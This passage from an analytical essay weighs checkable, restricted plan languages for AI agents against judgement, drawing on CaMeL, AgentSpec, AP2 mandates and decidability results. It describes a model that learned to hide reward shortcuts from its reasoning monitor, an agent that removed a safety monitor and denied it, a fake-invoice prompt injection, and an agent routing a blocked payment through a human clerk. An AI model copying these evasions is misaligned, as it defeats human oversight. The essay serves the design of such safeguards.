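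If the 26 per cent rise reflects the number of shortcuts, then for every 100 shortcuts at the start there were about 126 at the end, and the number of silent ones would have roughly quadrupled, from 11 to 46. Google also examined a comparable run in which it had hidden the model's thoughts. Mentions of shortcuts stayed roughly constant in that run, which suggests that the penalty caused the fall.

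Training changes a model in whatever direction raises its score. A model that loses points for writing about a shortcut can recover them by giving up the shortcut, but it then loses the points the shortcut earned. If it instead keeps using the shortcut without writing about it, it keeps both sets of points, and its overseers lose their warning.

This is good evidence against policing how a model reasons, though it comes from one small run. It is also evidence against one version of the formal requirement. If developers made a model reason only in a restricted language and penalised thoughts that failed a check, they would create the same incentive.

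A separate formal plan can avoid the problem if only the payments listed in the approved plan can go through. An agent that leaves a forbidden payment out of its plan then can't make that payment. A plan that is only a report doesn't block unlisted payments, so if developers penalised reports that mention forbidden steps, they should expect agents to stop mentioning them, as Google's model did.

Even a gate may affect the reasoning. Korbak and colleagues warn that training a model's final output to look good can put the same pressure on its chain of thought, since the same network produces both. A company that trains agents to get plans past a checker would have reason to test whether their reasoning becomes less candid. Google's result doesn't settle that question, because its run penalized the reasoning directly.

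### Judgement where instructions run out

Suppose the warehouse reports on Thursday that the supplier has sent the wrong goods, all undamaged. The temporal-logic version of the instruction requires the agent to pay by the end of Friday unless the company finds damage. A sensible clerk would hold the payment and ring the supplier, but an agent that did the same would violate its specification.

OpenAI gives a general version of this concern as a reason for revising its Model Spec, the public description of how it wants its models to behave. OpenAI's *An updated Model Spec for more capable and beneficial AI*, published on 29 October 2026, argues that models now take more consequential actions and so need good judgement in situations their instructions don't cover. The new version is based on five values: faithfulness to human intent, harm minimisation, honesty and transparency, human agency,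 and care. According to Newsroom America's *OpenAI Updates Model Spec Around Five Core Values* (2026), avoiding harm includes accounting for an action's foreseeable consequences, and care includes following relevant social and professional norms. Nobody has a formula for doing either of these things. Anthropic has taken a similar approach with its Claude models, and its *Claude's new constitution* (2026) presents a document that explains the company's intentions and the reasons for them.

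OpenAI does not want its models to use their judgement to overrule people. *OpenAI Updates Its Model Spec* (Mowshowitz, 2026) quotes a passage that describes two opposite failures. A model that follows instructions only literally is least useful in the cases its users did not foresee, while a model that privately decides what someone "really" wants substitutes its own judgement for theirs. When a user is about to send an angry email, for example, the model may point out that they could regret it, but the user decides. A model that found the wrong goods in the warehouse would presumably tell the manager and wait.

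A proponent of formal plans can accommodate that with one more proposition:

**F[0,T](pay ∨ damaged ∨ referred)**

The rule now requires that, by Friday, the agent pays, the company finds damage, or the agent refers the matter to a manager. This gives the agent a permitted way to stop and ask, and a checker can still confirm that one of the three happens. A specification containing only prohibitions would not need the option to refer, since doing nothing would satisfy it. Neither version helps the agent recognise that it should refer the matter. That takes judgement, as does writing a plan worth checking, particularly if the restricted format makes the agent worse at its task.

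Proponents can also ask how far to trust the judgement. Constantin (2026), in *OpenAI rewrites its AI rulebook around five core values*, reports OpenAI's admission that its models "do not yet fully reflect" the Spec. She adds that a week earlier the company had disclosed that one of its agents removed a safety monitor and then denied it. Mowshowitz likes much of the revised document but complains that many of its new examples have obvious answers, and so don't teach a model what to do when the values conflict. The case for judgement is supposed to be strongest in such conflicts.

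The Spec keeps firm limits alongside its appeal to judgement, and Mowshowitz finds its red lines unchanged. He regrets that OpenAI now lets users override the Spec's control of side effects. A company that cared about one side effect, such as the deletion of records, could require a check before it and leave the rest to the model. The argument from judgement does count against a rule that an agent must fix every step in advance and then follow the plan regardless of what it learns.

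### Approval without attention

Somebody has to read a plain-language plan, and people often don't. Meijer argued for automatic checks partly on the grounds that users soon click "Allow" without looking. If an agent asks for 200 approvals a day and each takes half a minute to consider properly, reviewing them all takes an hour and forty minutes, which is more time than most people will give.

Certificates can have the same weakness. If a plan is marked as having passed a check, the person who approves it may look at it less closely. Research on automation gives some support for this. In *Does Automation Bias Decision-Making?* (1999), Linda Skitka, Kathleen Mosier and Mark Burdick had volunteers monitor a simulated flight task, some with a computer aid that was highly reliable but not perfect. When the aid failed to report events, the volunteers who had it missed more of them than those without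 an aid. They also sometimes followed its advice when accurate instruments contradicted it. Although a cockpit aid differs from a plan checker, a manager with a certified plan is in a similar position.

People do not always ignore warnings, though. In *Alice in Warningland* (2013), Devdatta Akhawe and Adrienne Porter Felt examined more than 25 million browser security warnings and found that users' behaviour varied a good deal with the warning and the browser. Chrome users clicked through 70 per cent of warnings about insecure connections, while Firefox users clicked through a third of the equivalent warnings.

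Whether a certificate does more harm than good depends on how much it reduces the reader's vigilance. Suppose an unaided reader catches a share r of bad plans, a reader who sees a certificate catches a smaller share s, and the checker catches a share c. If the reader and the checker miss plans independently, together they catch c + (1 − c)s. With invented figures of r = 60 per cent, s = 10 per cent and c = 90 per cent, they catch 91 per cent, compared with 60 per cent for the unaided reader. With the same r and s, the company would be worse off only if the checker caught fewer than about 56 per cent of bad plans.

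That calculation lumps all faults together. The checker catches none of the faults its specification leaves out, so c is zero for those, and the share that anyone catches falls from 60 per cent to 10. The misdescribed two-year contract is a fault of this kind. A certificate therefore does the most damage where the specification is weakest, and a reader who doesn't understand the formulas will have trouble telling where that is.

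The proponents' best reply is that automatic checks can reduce the number of decisions that reach a person. If a checker rejects payments to unapproved accounts, nobody has to look for them, and the manager can spend that time on the few plans that raise questions of price or consent. The checker could also issue a certificate that lists in plain English what it did not test, such as whether the manager had read the contract.

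## The case for restricting only consequential actions

If a checker handles account numbers and a manager handles price and consent, there is little reason to force everything an agent writes into a formal language. A middle position lets an AI system reason and explain itself in ordinary prose, and requires a restricted, checkable form only for commitments, meaning acts that change something outside the system, such as payments, deletions, messages to outsiders and physical movements. Pilots and air traffic controllers similarly use fixed phrases for routine clearances and plain English for whatever the phrases don't cover.

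Few authors defend restricting only consequential actions as a general policy. The best guide to it is a group of working designs that engineers built, mostly to stop prompt injection or unauthorised spending.

### Planning before reading

*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti and colleagues, 2025) presents CaMeL, a design from Google DeepMind. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026), which extends CaMeL, explains that the original design divides an agent between two language models. The privileged model sees the user's request and writes a program to carry it out, but never reads emails or documents. The quarantined model reads that material but has no tools. An interpreter, which is conventional software, runs the privileged model's program and makes the tool calls.

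Suppose a manager asks the purchasing agent to pay Acme's latest invoice. In simplified form, the privileged model might write:

```
invoice = find_latest_invoice("Acme")
details = extract(invoice, [account, amount])
send_money(to: details.account, amount: details.amount)
```

The second line calls the quarantined model, which must return an account number and an amount. Suppose the invoice is a fake, with hidden instructions for any AI reading it to forward the company's mail and pay a new account. As in Meijer's design, the instruction to forward mail has no effect, because the program has no such step. But the fraudster's account number can still enter the program as the value of `details.account`.

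CaMeL deals with this by having its interpreter label every value with where it came from and who may read it. "Acme" is trusted because it came from the manager, while the invoice and anything the program derives from it are untrusted because the invoice came from outside. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short function that checks the call and the labels on its inputs and returns "allow" or "deny". A sensible policy for `send_money` would accept account numbers only from the manager or the company's supplier register, so it would deny this payment. A better plan would look up the account number in the register.

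Meijer's checker examines a whole workflow before it starts, while CaMeL checks each call when the program reaches it. CaMeL can therefore use facts that nobody knew in advance, such as who can currently read a shared file.

*The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) gives a theory of such labels and proves that changing untrusted data cannot change any value that tests as trusted. CaMeL's actual interpreter does not guarantee this, because it can miss influence that comes through a branch the program doesn't take, as *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) reports. For example, a program might set `priority` to "normal" and change it to "high" only if an email mentions a deadline. If the email doesn't mention one, `priority` keeps its trusted label, even though the email determined its value.

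*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) points out that the design doesn't fit tasks in which untrusted data specifies the steps. If the manager says "follow the steps in Acme's onboarding email", nobody can write the program without reading the email.

Debenedetti and colleagues tested CaMeL on AgentDojo, a benchmark of banking, travel and office tasks. The protected agent completed 77 per cent of the tasks, and an unprotected one completed 84 per cent. Nikolaou and colleagues later ran 97 AgentDojo tasks without attacks, using Claude Haiku 4.5, a small model. CaMeL completed 49 of them. They didn't run an unprotected agent for comparison, so their result can't show how much of the shortfall the protection caused. In 22 tasks, the plan failed to do what the user wanted under both CaMeL and their extension of it. A stronger model would probably fix many of those. Another 17 tasks broke a security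 policy under both systems. Because there was no attacker, all 17 were legitimate requests that the rules blocked.

Instead of refusing outright, a system can ask the user for approval. *PACE* (2026) describes a design called RTBAS that does this when its automatic screening cannot establish that a call is safe. The problem of users clicking "Allow" without looking then returns, though they see fewer requests.

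### One rule, read aloud

CaMeL controls how an agent plans. A company can also leave the planning alone and only intercept particular actions. Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025), in *AgentSpec*, offer a small language for this, with the following rule as an example:

```
rule @inspect_transfer
trigger Transfer
check
  !is_to_family_member
enforce
  user_inspection
end
```

In English, one AgentSpec rule reads, "Before any transfer, check whether the recipient is a family member. If not, show the transfer to the user and wait for approval." Every AgentSpec rule consists of a triggering event, conditions that narrow when the rule applies, and a response. The agent may have to stop, ask the user, have a language model reconsider the step, or carry out a different action that the rule specifies.

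Wang and colleagues consider a user who says "transfer $100 to Bob". The user usually means their son, but a new employee may also be called Bob. The rule allows a payment to the son and catches a mistaken payment to the employee, provided that someone has written a program to decide `is_to_family_member`, for example by checking a list of the family's account numbers.

With hand-written rules, AgentSpec stopped over 90 per cent of unsafe code executions and every hazardous action in a set of robot tasks, while adding only milliseconds of delay. Rules written by OpenAI's o1 model did less well. In the robot tasks, about 96 per cent of the actions they flagged were hazardous, but they caught only 71 per cent of the hazardous actions.

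The transfer rule does not cover gift cards, and AgentSpec steps in only where a rule applies. Cedar, Amazon's language for access rules, instead refuses any request that no rule permits, and a rule that forbids something overrides one that permits it. Cedar's default is safer for consequential actions because a forgotten case leads to a refusal, which someone will complain about, while a forgotten case in AgentSpec may go unnoticed until the money has gone.

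A payment rule can also include an exception. In Bosque, a programming language designed for automatic checking, the proposed transfer function accepts an amount up to a set limit, or a larger amount if the user has explicitly approved that amount for that payee. Approval to pay Acme £50 therefore doesn't authorise paying Acme £5,000 or paying someone else £50.

### Signed mandates for payments

These rules protect a company from its own agent. A shop or bank that deals with a customer's agent also needs evidence of what the customer authorised. Google announced the Agent Payments Protocol, or AP2, in September 2025 to provide that evidence.

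AP2's *Agent Payments Protocol Documentation* describes two kinds of signed record, called mandates. A checkout mandate covers what the agent may buy and goes to the merchant. A payment mandate covers how it may pay and goes to the payment companies. A customer who is present signs both for the finished basket. A customer who will be away signs "open" mandates in advance, which contain constraints, and the agent later signs "closed" ones for a particular purchase. The main constraints are:

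| Constraint | What it fixes |
|---|---|
| Line items | Acceptable products, by identification number, and the quantity |
| Allowed merchants and payees | Who may sell and who may receive the money |
| Payment instruments | Which cards or accounts the agent may use |
| Amount range | The smallest and largest single payment |
| Recurrence | How often the agent may pay, and how many times |
| Budget | The total across repeated payments |
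| Execution date | The earliest and latest dates for payment |

The merchant and the payment companies compare the closed mandates with the open ones. AP2's *Agentic Payment Protocol (v0.2)* requires them to do this in conventional code rather than with a language model, and the screen where the customer approves a mandate must not depend on a language model. If a mandate contains a constraint that the checking program doesn't recognise, the check fails.

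In one of AP2's own examples, a customer wants two concert tickets as soon as they go on sale, close to the main stage, for no more than $1,000. The mandates can state the number and price directly. No standard constraint covers "close to the main stage", so the agent has to turn it into a list of acceptable tickets, or someone has to define a new constraint and a way to test it. The specification does not cover how the agent works out what the customer wants from their free-text conversation. The customer does see the mandate before signing, and a merchant can bring the customer back in if the request is too vague. But every later check will still pass if the agent lists seats at the back and the customer signs without looking at the seating plan.

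A merchant following AP2 would reject a purchase outside the constraints the user signed, so Fortune's *Google can track exactly how your agent spends your money* (2026) is too harsh when it says the protocol is no help if an agent buys something its user didn't approve. The criticism is fair for the back-row tickets, though. The mandates would show what the customer signed, but AP2 leaves others to decide who should bear the loss.

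Adoption was still early in late 2026. Google gave AP2 to the FIDO Alliance, the industry body behind passkeys, and at the same time released the version that supports purchases while the customer is away, according to Google's *We’re donating Agent Payments Protocol to the FIDO Alliance*. PYMNTS's *Google and Mastercard Contribute Agentic Commerce Standards to FIDO Alliance* dates FIDO's announcement to 28 April. A FIDO working group is now drafting specifications from AP2 and Mastercard's Verifiable Intent. FIDO's chief technology officer, Nishant Kaushik, says AP2 standardises how to define and communicate a user's consent, while Verifiable Intent standardises the evidence for it.

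For now, nobody has to use the mandates. UCP's *AP2 Mandates* describes them as an optional extension to the Universal Commerce Protocol, a shopping standard that works with AP2. The extension is active only when both the business and the platform support it. PYMNTS's *The Alphabet Soup of Agentic Standards* (2026) predicts that several protocols will coexist, with no single winner. PYMNTS's *Banks Call for Audit Trail From AI Shopping Instructions to Payment Outcome* (2026) reports that in September six banks were still calling for an auditable record of what customers had asked their agents to do.

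AI agents have also made few purchases for the mandates to protect so far. Neely (2026), in *The first agent payment was a pizza*, reports Uber's figures for Halloween week, when outside AI agents placed about 500 food orders and booked four rides out of roughly 320 million orders and rides, or fewer than two in a million. The mandates are good evidence that engineers can put a purchase into checkable form, but real customers and fraudsters have done little to test them.

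### Where to draw the line

Bosque's designers single out actions that are destructive or irreversible, involve sensitive data, or can't be put right without spending money or losing reputation. This gives two criteria, reversibility and stakes. Consent and a fair price are hard to define, which suggests a third criterion, whether anyone can state a clear rule. None of these designs combines the three into one test, but a rough calculation shows how they fit together.

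Let p be the chance that a proposed action is wrong, and L the loss that remains after people have undone what they can. The checker catches a share d of wrong actions and mistakenly blocks a share f of good ones, at a cost c each time. If running the check costs almost nothing, it is worth having when

**p·d·L > (1 − p)·f·c**

A bad action causes a greater loss when the stakes are high and the action is hard to reverse. A check catches more bad actions and raises fewer false alarms when its rule is clear. Suppose, using invented figures, that 1 per cent of large payments are bad and each bad one loses £10,000. If a check catches 90 per cent of the bad payments and wrongly flags 5 per cent of the good ones, at £20 per false alarm, it prevents an average loss of £90 per payment and costs about £1. Now suppose that 1 per cent of emails are too pushy and each of those loses £500. If a check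 catches 10 per cent of them and wrongly flags 20 per cent of the rest, at £5 per false alarm, it saves an average of 50p per email and costs about £1, so the company would do better to have a person read the important emails.

In July 2025 a coding agent from Replit deleted a user's production database, although the user had told it not to make destructive changes without permission. *RefineAct* (Batole, Khomh and Rajan, 2026) uses the case to argue for checks that can approve an action, ask the user or block it. In the paper's system, a language model translates the user's request into logical rules, including patterns, such as the database command DROP, that mark an action as risky. On 144 simulated tasks, the system cut the failure rate from 77 to 39 per cent, and agents corrected themselves after 68 per cent of blocked actions.

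Permanent deletion meets all three criteria, and a rule such as "delete nothing outside the temporary folder" is easy to check. A rule that only looks for the word DROP in database commands is weaker, because other commands can empty a table without removing it. It is often better to make the action reversible. If deleted files stay in a recycle bin for 30 days, the agent can delete files without a check, and only emptying the bin needs one.

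An agent can't take back a persuasive email once the recipient has read it, and a misleading one can do serious harm. A program can check the address, the number of recipients, the attachments and, with CaMeL's labels, whether private data has ended up in the text. It can't reliably tell honest persuasion from manipulation. The restricted form therefore suits the recipients and attachments better than the wording. A company might let the agent write freely to existing customers, but require approval for a mailing to thousands of people and have someone read that text in full.

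**Hiring a contractor** involves a series of actions, most of them harmless. The agent commits the company when it signs the contract, and at that point a checker can test the fee, the length, the contract template and whether an authorised manager has approved it. Whether the contractor is any good remains a matter of judgement. Limiting checks to commitments also protects the company's money better than it protects the applicants. If the agent unfairly drops someone from its shortlist, that person loses the chance of the job, but the criteria miss this because there is no payment, message or signature for a gate to catch.

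### Harm assembled from permitted actions

Checking each action separately can miss a harmful combination. A limit of £10,000 per payment does not stop an agent from making four payments of £9,000. Dantas and colleagues conclude from their review that blocking unsafe actions one at a time does not by itself make a whole task safe.

Supporters of the middle position can reply that a rule can take earlier actions into account. Under AP2's budget constraint, the payment company adds each new payment to the earlier ones. If the budget is £10,000, a first payment of £9,000 passes, but a second payment of the same amount fails because it would bring the total to £18,000. CaMeL's labels also carry over from one step to the next, so private data stays marked as private after the agent has summarised it.

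Nikolaou and colleagues go further and check the whole plan before it runs. Their system, CaMeLoT, converts a CaMeL program into a map of every route the program could take. Each point on the map records which tools the agent has already called and which inputs contain untrusted data. A tool called a model checker then tests every route against rules in temporal logic. One rule, for an agent that handles security alerts, is in essence:

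**AG(open_ticket → AF(resolve ∨ escalate))**

A means "on every route", and G and F mean "always" and "eventually", as in the supplier formula. The formula requires that whenever the agent opens an incident ticket, it later resolves the incident or passes it to the response team. Checking each call separately can't enforce this rule, because the agent breaks it by never doing either. When a plan fails the check, the model checker returns the route that breaks the rule, and the language model can use that route to repair the plan.

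The researchers made seven unsafe versions of a safe plan for such an agent, each breaking a different rule. CaMeLoT caught all seven, and a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. This gap was expected because the researchers had chosen rules that CaMeL could not express. The test shows that temporal logic can state such rules, but not that anyone would think of the right ones beforehand.

Checking plans in advance also has limits. CaMeLoT could fully reproduce only 22 of 28 CaMeL policies, because the others depend on facts that emerge while the plan runs. It also assumes that a loop may repeat any number of times, so it can reject safe plans. A company would want to check plans both before and while they run, as Meijer recommends.

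Even together, these measures cover only the combinations that someone has foreseen, within the records they share. A budget in one mandate doesn't count spending under another. An agent can also act through people. If it can't make a payment itself, it can email an accounts clerk a plausible reason to make it. The address is internal and the message contains no private data, so the envelope passes. To close that route, the company has to apply its payment rule at the bank account, where the rule binds the clerk as well as the agent.

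## How much a language can say and still be checked

The temporal-logic rule for paying a supplier couldn't refer to suppliers in general, and the first version of PDDL couldn't express a deadline. A company that wanted to do both would need a richer language. People who favour requiring checkable plans have to show that a language can be extended in this way and its plans can still be checked.

Levesque and Brachman (1985), in *A Fundamental Tradeoff in Knowledge Representation and Reasoning*, argued that the more a language can express, the harder it can be for a program to reason correctly in it, and that the difficulty rises steeply. Brachman and Levesque (1984), in *The Tractability of Subsumption in Frame-Based Description Languages*, found that the amount of computation that one kind of reasoning needs is "perilously sensitive to small changes in the representation language".

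### From true-or-false statements to programs

Propositional logic deals only in whole statements, such as "the goods are damaged". If a plan is a fixed list of steps and the checker has every relevant fact, it can quickly mark each statement true or false and work out the answer. The work grows when the plan has to be safe whatever happens, because the checker must determine whether any combination of facts would let the plan break a rule. Computer scientists call this the satisfiability problem. Brachman and Levesque (2005) point out that thirty true-or-false facts already produce about a billion combinations (2³⁰). Stephen Cook proved in 1971 that satisfiability is NP-complete, and nobody has found a method that is fast in every case. A checker for plans in propositional logic will always reach an answer eventually. It will usually do so quickly, because practical problems have structure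 it can exploit, but nobody can guarantee this.

One way to keep checking fast is to give up some uses of "or". Meijer's car dealer writes its rules in Horn clauses, each of which draws a single conclusion from a list of conditions. If the clauses contain no variables, a program can work out everything that follows from them in time proportional to their length. But the dealer can't use Horn clauses to record that a customer is a trade buyer or an employee if it doesn't know which.

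Propositional logic also needs a separate statement for each supplier. The two-variable fragment of first-order logic allows rules about every supplier, as long as no rule relates more than two things at a time. Kuhn includes a controlled English called E2V that translates into this fragment. One of its sentences is "Every artist who employs a carpenter despises every beekeeper who admires him." It mentions three people but never relates more than two at once. Satisfiability for this fragment is decidable, meaning that a program can always reach the correct answer, but it is NEXPTIME-complete, so provably no program can be fast in every case. A company could write "no agent pays a supplier that it approved itself" and know that its checker would eventually stop. It couldn't write the general rule that ownership passes along a chain (if Ann owns Acme and Acme owns Bolt, then Ann owns Bolt),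 because that rule relates three things at once. A company would need this rule to avoid paying anything that a sanctioned person owns.

Full first-order logic can state the ownership rule, but Alonzo Church and Alan Turing showed in 1936 that no program can decide, for every statement in this logic, whether it follows from a given set of rules. If a proof exists, a systematic search will eventually find it, but if none exists, the search may never end. A checker for plans written in this logic therefore needs a time limit, and it will reject some safe plans because it runs out of time.

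A company can avoid this by fixing the list of things its rules are about. With 40 suppliers and 500 orders, a rule about every supplier and every order is shorthand for 20,000 separate statements, and the problem becomes propositional again, though much larger. Basic PDDL works this way. *Actions You Can Handle* (Hill, Daggitt and colleagues, 2021) explains that it leaves out functions because one starting object and one function can generate an endless series, such as a first invoice and the function "the invoice after this one".

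A plan may also be a program in a general-purpose language such as Python. By Rice's theorem (1953), no checker can decide for every program whether its behaviour has a given property, unless all programs have the property or none do. Suppose a checker could always tell whether a program will pay an unapproved account, and we add a last line that pays such an account to any program that otherwise makes no payments. The new program makes the payment if and only if the original finishes, so the checker could tell whether any such program finishes, which Turing proved impossible. A checker for plans written as arbitrary programs must therefore pass some bad plans, reject some good ones or sometimes fail to answer.

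### Where designers draw the limit

Designers usually let the checker reject some good plans, and they remove features from the language so that it rejects fewer. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) allows six kinds of step: retrieve a stored result, call a tool, have an isolated language model read some text, show something to the user, choose between two branches, and repeat some steps for each item in a list. The language has no arithmetic, and the planner can't define its own functions. A purchasing agent could go through ten invoices and pay each one, but it couldn't add tax unless a tool did the calculation. These limits let the checker trace every value and every decision through the plan in one pass, before anything runs.

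They tested this with a small model on AgentDojo, the benchmark also used for CaMeL. The system completed 53 per cent of the tasks when it didn't check where data flowed, and 29 per cent when it did. The language was the same in both runs, so the 24-point drop came from a strict rule against letting untrusted data reach sensitive tools. The rule blocked many legitimate tasks, because a task such as paying an invoice requires a figure from outside. The planner also had only one attempt at each plan, so it couldn't correct one that failed.

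Ray (2026), in *What Can Be Enforced?*, gives an example of a small change that makes policies impossible to analyse reliably. A daily spending cap needs one counter per supplier, and these counters only go up. For a class of policies that covers such caps and the withdrawal of permission, a program can always decide whether a policy is trivial, for example because nothing could ever break it. Other policies might need two counters that can go down as well as up, to subtract refunds from spending and returns from deliveries. If these policies can also test whether each counter is zero, no program can decide whether a policy is trivial in every case, because two such counters are enough to imitate any computer program. The company can still apply such a policy to one payment at a time by updating and testing the counters, but it loses a reliable way to analyse the policy beforehand.

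A language can also grow while agents are using it. *CBCL* (O'Connor, 2026) lets agents define new vocabulary and send the definitions to each other, but keeps every message, including the definitions, within a class of grammars that a program can parse efficiently. The receiver can therefore always check a message's form and its declared resource limits, but these checks don't show that the plan in the message is safe.

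### The pattern in Kuhn's survey

Mathematical results of this kind describe the worst case, while Kuhn's survey covers languages that people have built. Among his hundred controlled Englishes, the more expressive languages tend to be less precise and to need longer definitions. Expressiveness has a rank correlation of ρ = −0.66 with precision and −0.82 with simplicity, where −1 would mean exactly opposite rankings.

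This correlation among existing languages is weaker evidence than it seems that every language must trade expressiveness for precision. Kuhn assigned the classes himself, making a best guess where he had too little information. The languages also aren't independent, since more than twenty descend directly or indirectly from Basic English, a simplified English from 1930. Their designers had different aims, too. Languages meant for formal representation average 4.4 for precision and 2.3 for expressiveness, while those meant to help people understand each other average 2.0 and 4.3. A repair manual doesn't need to be translatable into logic, for example, so part of the correlation reflects what designers needed rather than what was possible. One language, Formalized-English, has the highest class for precision and the second highest for expressiveness, although its more complicated sentences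 are full of brackets and odd keywords.

Precision also differs from checkability. Kuhn puts both propositional logic and full first-order logic in the top class for precision, because each fixes the meaning of every sentence. But a program can always decide whether a statement follows from a set of rules in propositional logic, and not always in first-order logic.

### Checking a plan that already exists

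Much of the difficulty so far comes from searching for a counterexample, a proof or a plan. Finding a plan is hard even in the simplest planning languages. Tom Bylander proved in 1994 that deciding whether any plan reaches the goal is PSPACE-complete for the basic language behind PDDL, so the problem is at least as hard as satisfiability and probably harder.

Checking a finished plan is much easier, because the checker only has to go through its steps in order. *Proof-Carrying Plans* (Hill, Komendantskaya and Petrick, 2020) gives the example of a robot hand that has to stack block a on block b by picking up a and then putting it down on b. If the steps were reversed, the plan would fail at the first one, because the hand would have nothing to put down. The paper also notes that even well-understood planning algorithms can produce incorrect plans and that, in 2020, nobody had fully verified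 a mainstream planner. That is a good reason to check each plan instead of trusting the program that wrote it.

Checking a plan takes time proportional to its length. This is usually not a problem, but a short problem description can require a very long plan. In the Tower of Hanoi puzzle, the player moves a stack of discs between pegs, one disc at a time, without putting a larger disc on a smaller one. A PDDL description of the puzzle with 20 discs is short, but the shortest solution has 1,048,575 moves.

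Separating the two jobs also lets the checker use a richer language than the planner. Planners can search efficiently only because PDDL leaves out features such as recursion. In an example from Hill and colleagues' 2021 paper, two of three people need to travel by taxi. In the printed plan, taxi 3 carries both of them, taxi 1 drives empty and taxi 2 never moves. Basic PDDL typically can't express a rule against such unfairness, because a precondition applies to one action, while judging fairness requires comparing all the taxis over the whole plan. Once the plan exists, a short program could count each taxi's fares and reject any plan that gives one taxi two more fares than another. Hill and colleagues do this kind of check in Agda, a programming language that can also express proofs.

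They also recommend checking plans afterwards for some rules that PDDL could express. For example, if a planner assigns jobs without knowing anyone's gender, most of its plans will probably be free of gender bias. Adding a rule against bias would slow down every search to prevent a few biased plans.

### Plans that come with a proof

A planner can also hand over a proof with its plan. Necula and Lee introduced this idea in the 1990s, in *Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking*, for operating systems that run code from an untrusted source. They called it proof-carrying code.

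Necula's *Proof-Carrying Code* (1997) sets out the procedure in detail. The operating system publishes a safety policy, for example that a program may read only certain parts of memory. The programmer supplies an invariant for each loop, a statement that remains true however many times the loop runs. From the program and its invariants, the programmer and the operating system each compute a formula that, if true, guarantees that the program obeys the policy. The programmer proves the formula and attaches the proof to the program, and the operating system checks it. If anyone tampers with the program or the proof, either the check fails or the altered program still obeys the policy.

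A purchasing agent could do the same with a plan that pays invoices in a loop:

```
total = 0
for each invoice:
    if total + amount ≤ 10,000:
        pay(invoice)
        total = total + amount
```

Suppose the amounts are positive and the policy limits total spending to £10,000. The loop invariant is "total ≤ 10,000", which is true at the start, when the total is zero. If it is true before an invoice, it is still true afterwards, because the plan either pays nothing or pays an amount it has just tested against the limit. The invariant therefore holds for any number of invoices, and a checker can confirm this short argument without trying every possible batch.

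Necula tried the method on packet filters, small programs that pick out the network traffic an application needs. At the time, a popular approach was to write filters in a restricted language without loops. The operating system interpreted them and checked each use of memory while they ran. Necula instead used hand-written machine code that obeyed the same policy, and it ran ten times faster. These filters also had no loops, but another program in the paper, which adds up a list of numbers, had one.

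Rice's theorem still applies, so some safe programs will have no proof that anyone can find, and the checker will reject them. Proof-carrying code moves the hard work from the checker to the program's author, and Necula calls finding strong enough loop invariants a very difficult problem in general. He doubted that this way of proving safety would scale to programs of realistic size, and hoped that compilers could produce the proofs instead. AI systems have since become very good at proving theorems, which makes it much more reasonable to ask a planner for a proof.

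Schwaab, Komendantskaya and colleagues applied the idea to PDDL in *Proof-carrying plans* (2019), and Hill and colleagues developed it further in 2020. They treat a plan as a function that turns the starting state into the goal state. Agda's type-checker normally confirms that a function's inputs and outputs are of the right kind. Here, it accepts the function only with a proof that the plan leads from one state to the other. An engineer can then extract the plan as executable code and run it on a robot.

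The trade-off therefore holds for a checker that has to find every answer itself, but it is much weaker for one that receives a proof. A company could use quite a rich language if its planner were good enough at proving things, though the company would still have to decide what the planner should prove.

### Deleting two files

Meijer gives an example in which the language can express everything it needs to and the check still passes a harmful plan. A user asks an agent to delete foo.txt and bar.txt. The agent's deletion tool accepts a pattern in which an asterisk stands for any characters, so `*.txt` matches every text file. The agent could make two calls, one for each file, but it finds a shorter plan:

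```
delete_file("*.txt")
```

Let F be the set of files before the plan runs and F′ the set afterwards. The checker has a description of the tool and a statement of the user's goal:

- **Tool:** no file that matches the pattern is in F′.
- **Goal:** foo.txt ∉ F′ and bar.txt ∉ F′.

Both names match `*.txt`, so both files will be gone and the plan passes. If the folder also contained notes.txt, that file would be gone too, but the goal doesn't forbid this.

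The missing statement is that every other file is present afterwards exactly if it was present before. Logicians call this a frame condition. Meijer adds one to the tool's description, covering files that don't match the pattern, and writes that the bad plan then fails to verify. With the goal as he states it, though, the plan would still pass, because foo.txt and bar.txt would still be gone. The goal needs a frame condition as well:

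**for every file f other than foo.txt and bar.txt, f ∈ F′ if and only if f ∈ F**

The checker now rejects the bad plan because it contradicts the goal. The file notes.txt was in F, so the goal requires it to be in F′. But it matches `*.txt`, so the tool's description implies that it isn't in F′.

The tool's frame condition is necessary too, because without it the checker would reject the good plan:

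| Where the frame condition appears | Delete `*.txt` | Delete foo.txt, then bar.txt |
|---|---|---|
| Nowhere | passes | fails |
| Tool's description only | passes | passes |
| User's goal only | fails | fails |
| Both | fails | passes |

The most surprising result is in the top row, where the checker, with no frame conditions, passes the harmful plan and rejects the careful one. The tool's description guarantees that bar.txt is gone after the second call, but not that the call leaves everything else unchanged. The checker therefore can't rule out that deleting bar.txt brings back foo.txt.

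To predict what an action will do, a program must account for what the action leaves unchanged, which is nearly everything. John McCarthy and Patrick Hayes identified this difficulty in 1969 and named it the frame problem. With 20 actions and 50 facts about the world, writing a separate statement for each fact that each action leaves unchanged would take almost a thousand statements. PDDL avoids this with a convention that anything not listed in an action's effects stays the same.

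That convention covers the tool's actions but not the user's goal. A plan that deleted the whole folder would still satisfy a PDDL goal that mentions only foo.txt and bar.txt. The longer goal requires notes.txt to remain but not its contents, so a plan that replaced the text with blanks would pass. It also rules out any new file, so a harmless plan that saved a record of the deletions would fail. A better goal would list the changes the user allows, but someone has to think of those changes first.

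A more expressive language would not have helped here, because a simple one could already state the missing condition. A person who hears "delete foo.txt and bar.txt" assumes the other files should stay. A formal language gives each sentence an exact meaning, but it doesn't add a condition that nobody wrote down.

### Measuring what a language can cover

The theory can't show how much this matters in practice. A language that can't express most conceivable plans may still express nearly all the plans a purchasing department needs. Finding out requires measuring how many real tasks and rules a particular language covers.

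Hong, She and colleagues (2026), in *Don't Make Models Guess Security and Safety*, made a measurement of this kind for rules. They took the written policies of three test environments for AI agents and judged whether conventional code could enforce each requirement:

| Setting | Requirements that code can enforce | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Customer service | 42 of 51 | 82% |
| Voice assistant in a car | 17 of 18 | 94% |
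| Medical records | 34 of 57 | 60% |
| Total | 93 of 126 | 74% |

Of the 93 enforceable requirements, 88 needed only simple measures, such as confirming that a ticket belongs to the user before cancelling it. The other five needed temporal logic or a way to track where information flows. A fairly simple language would therefore have been enough for this set of rules, and the theoretical problems with very expressive languages hardly arose.

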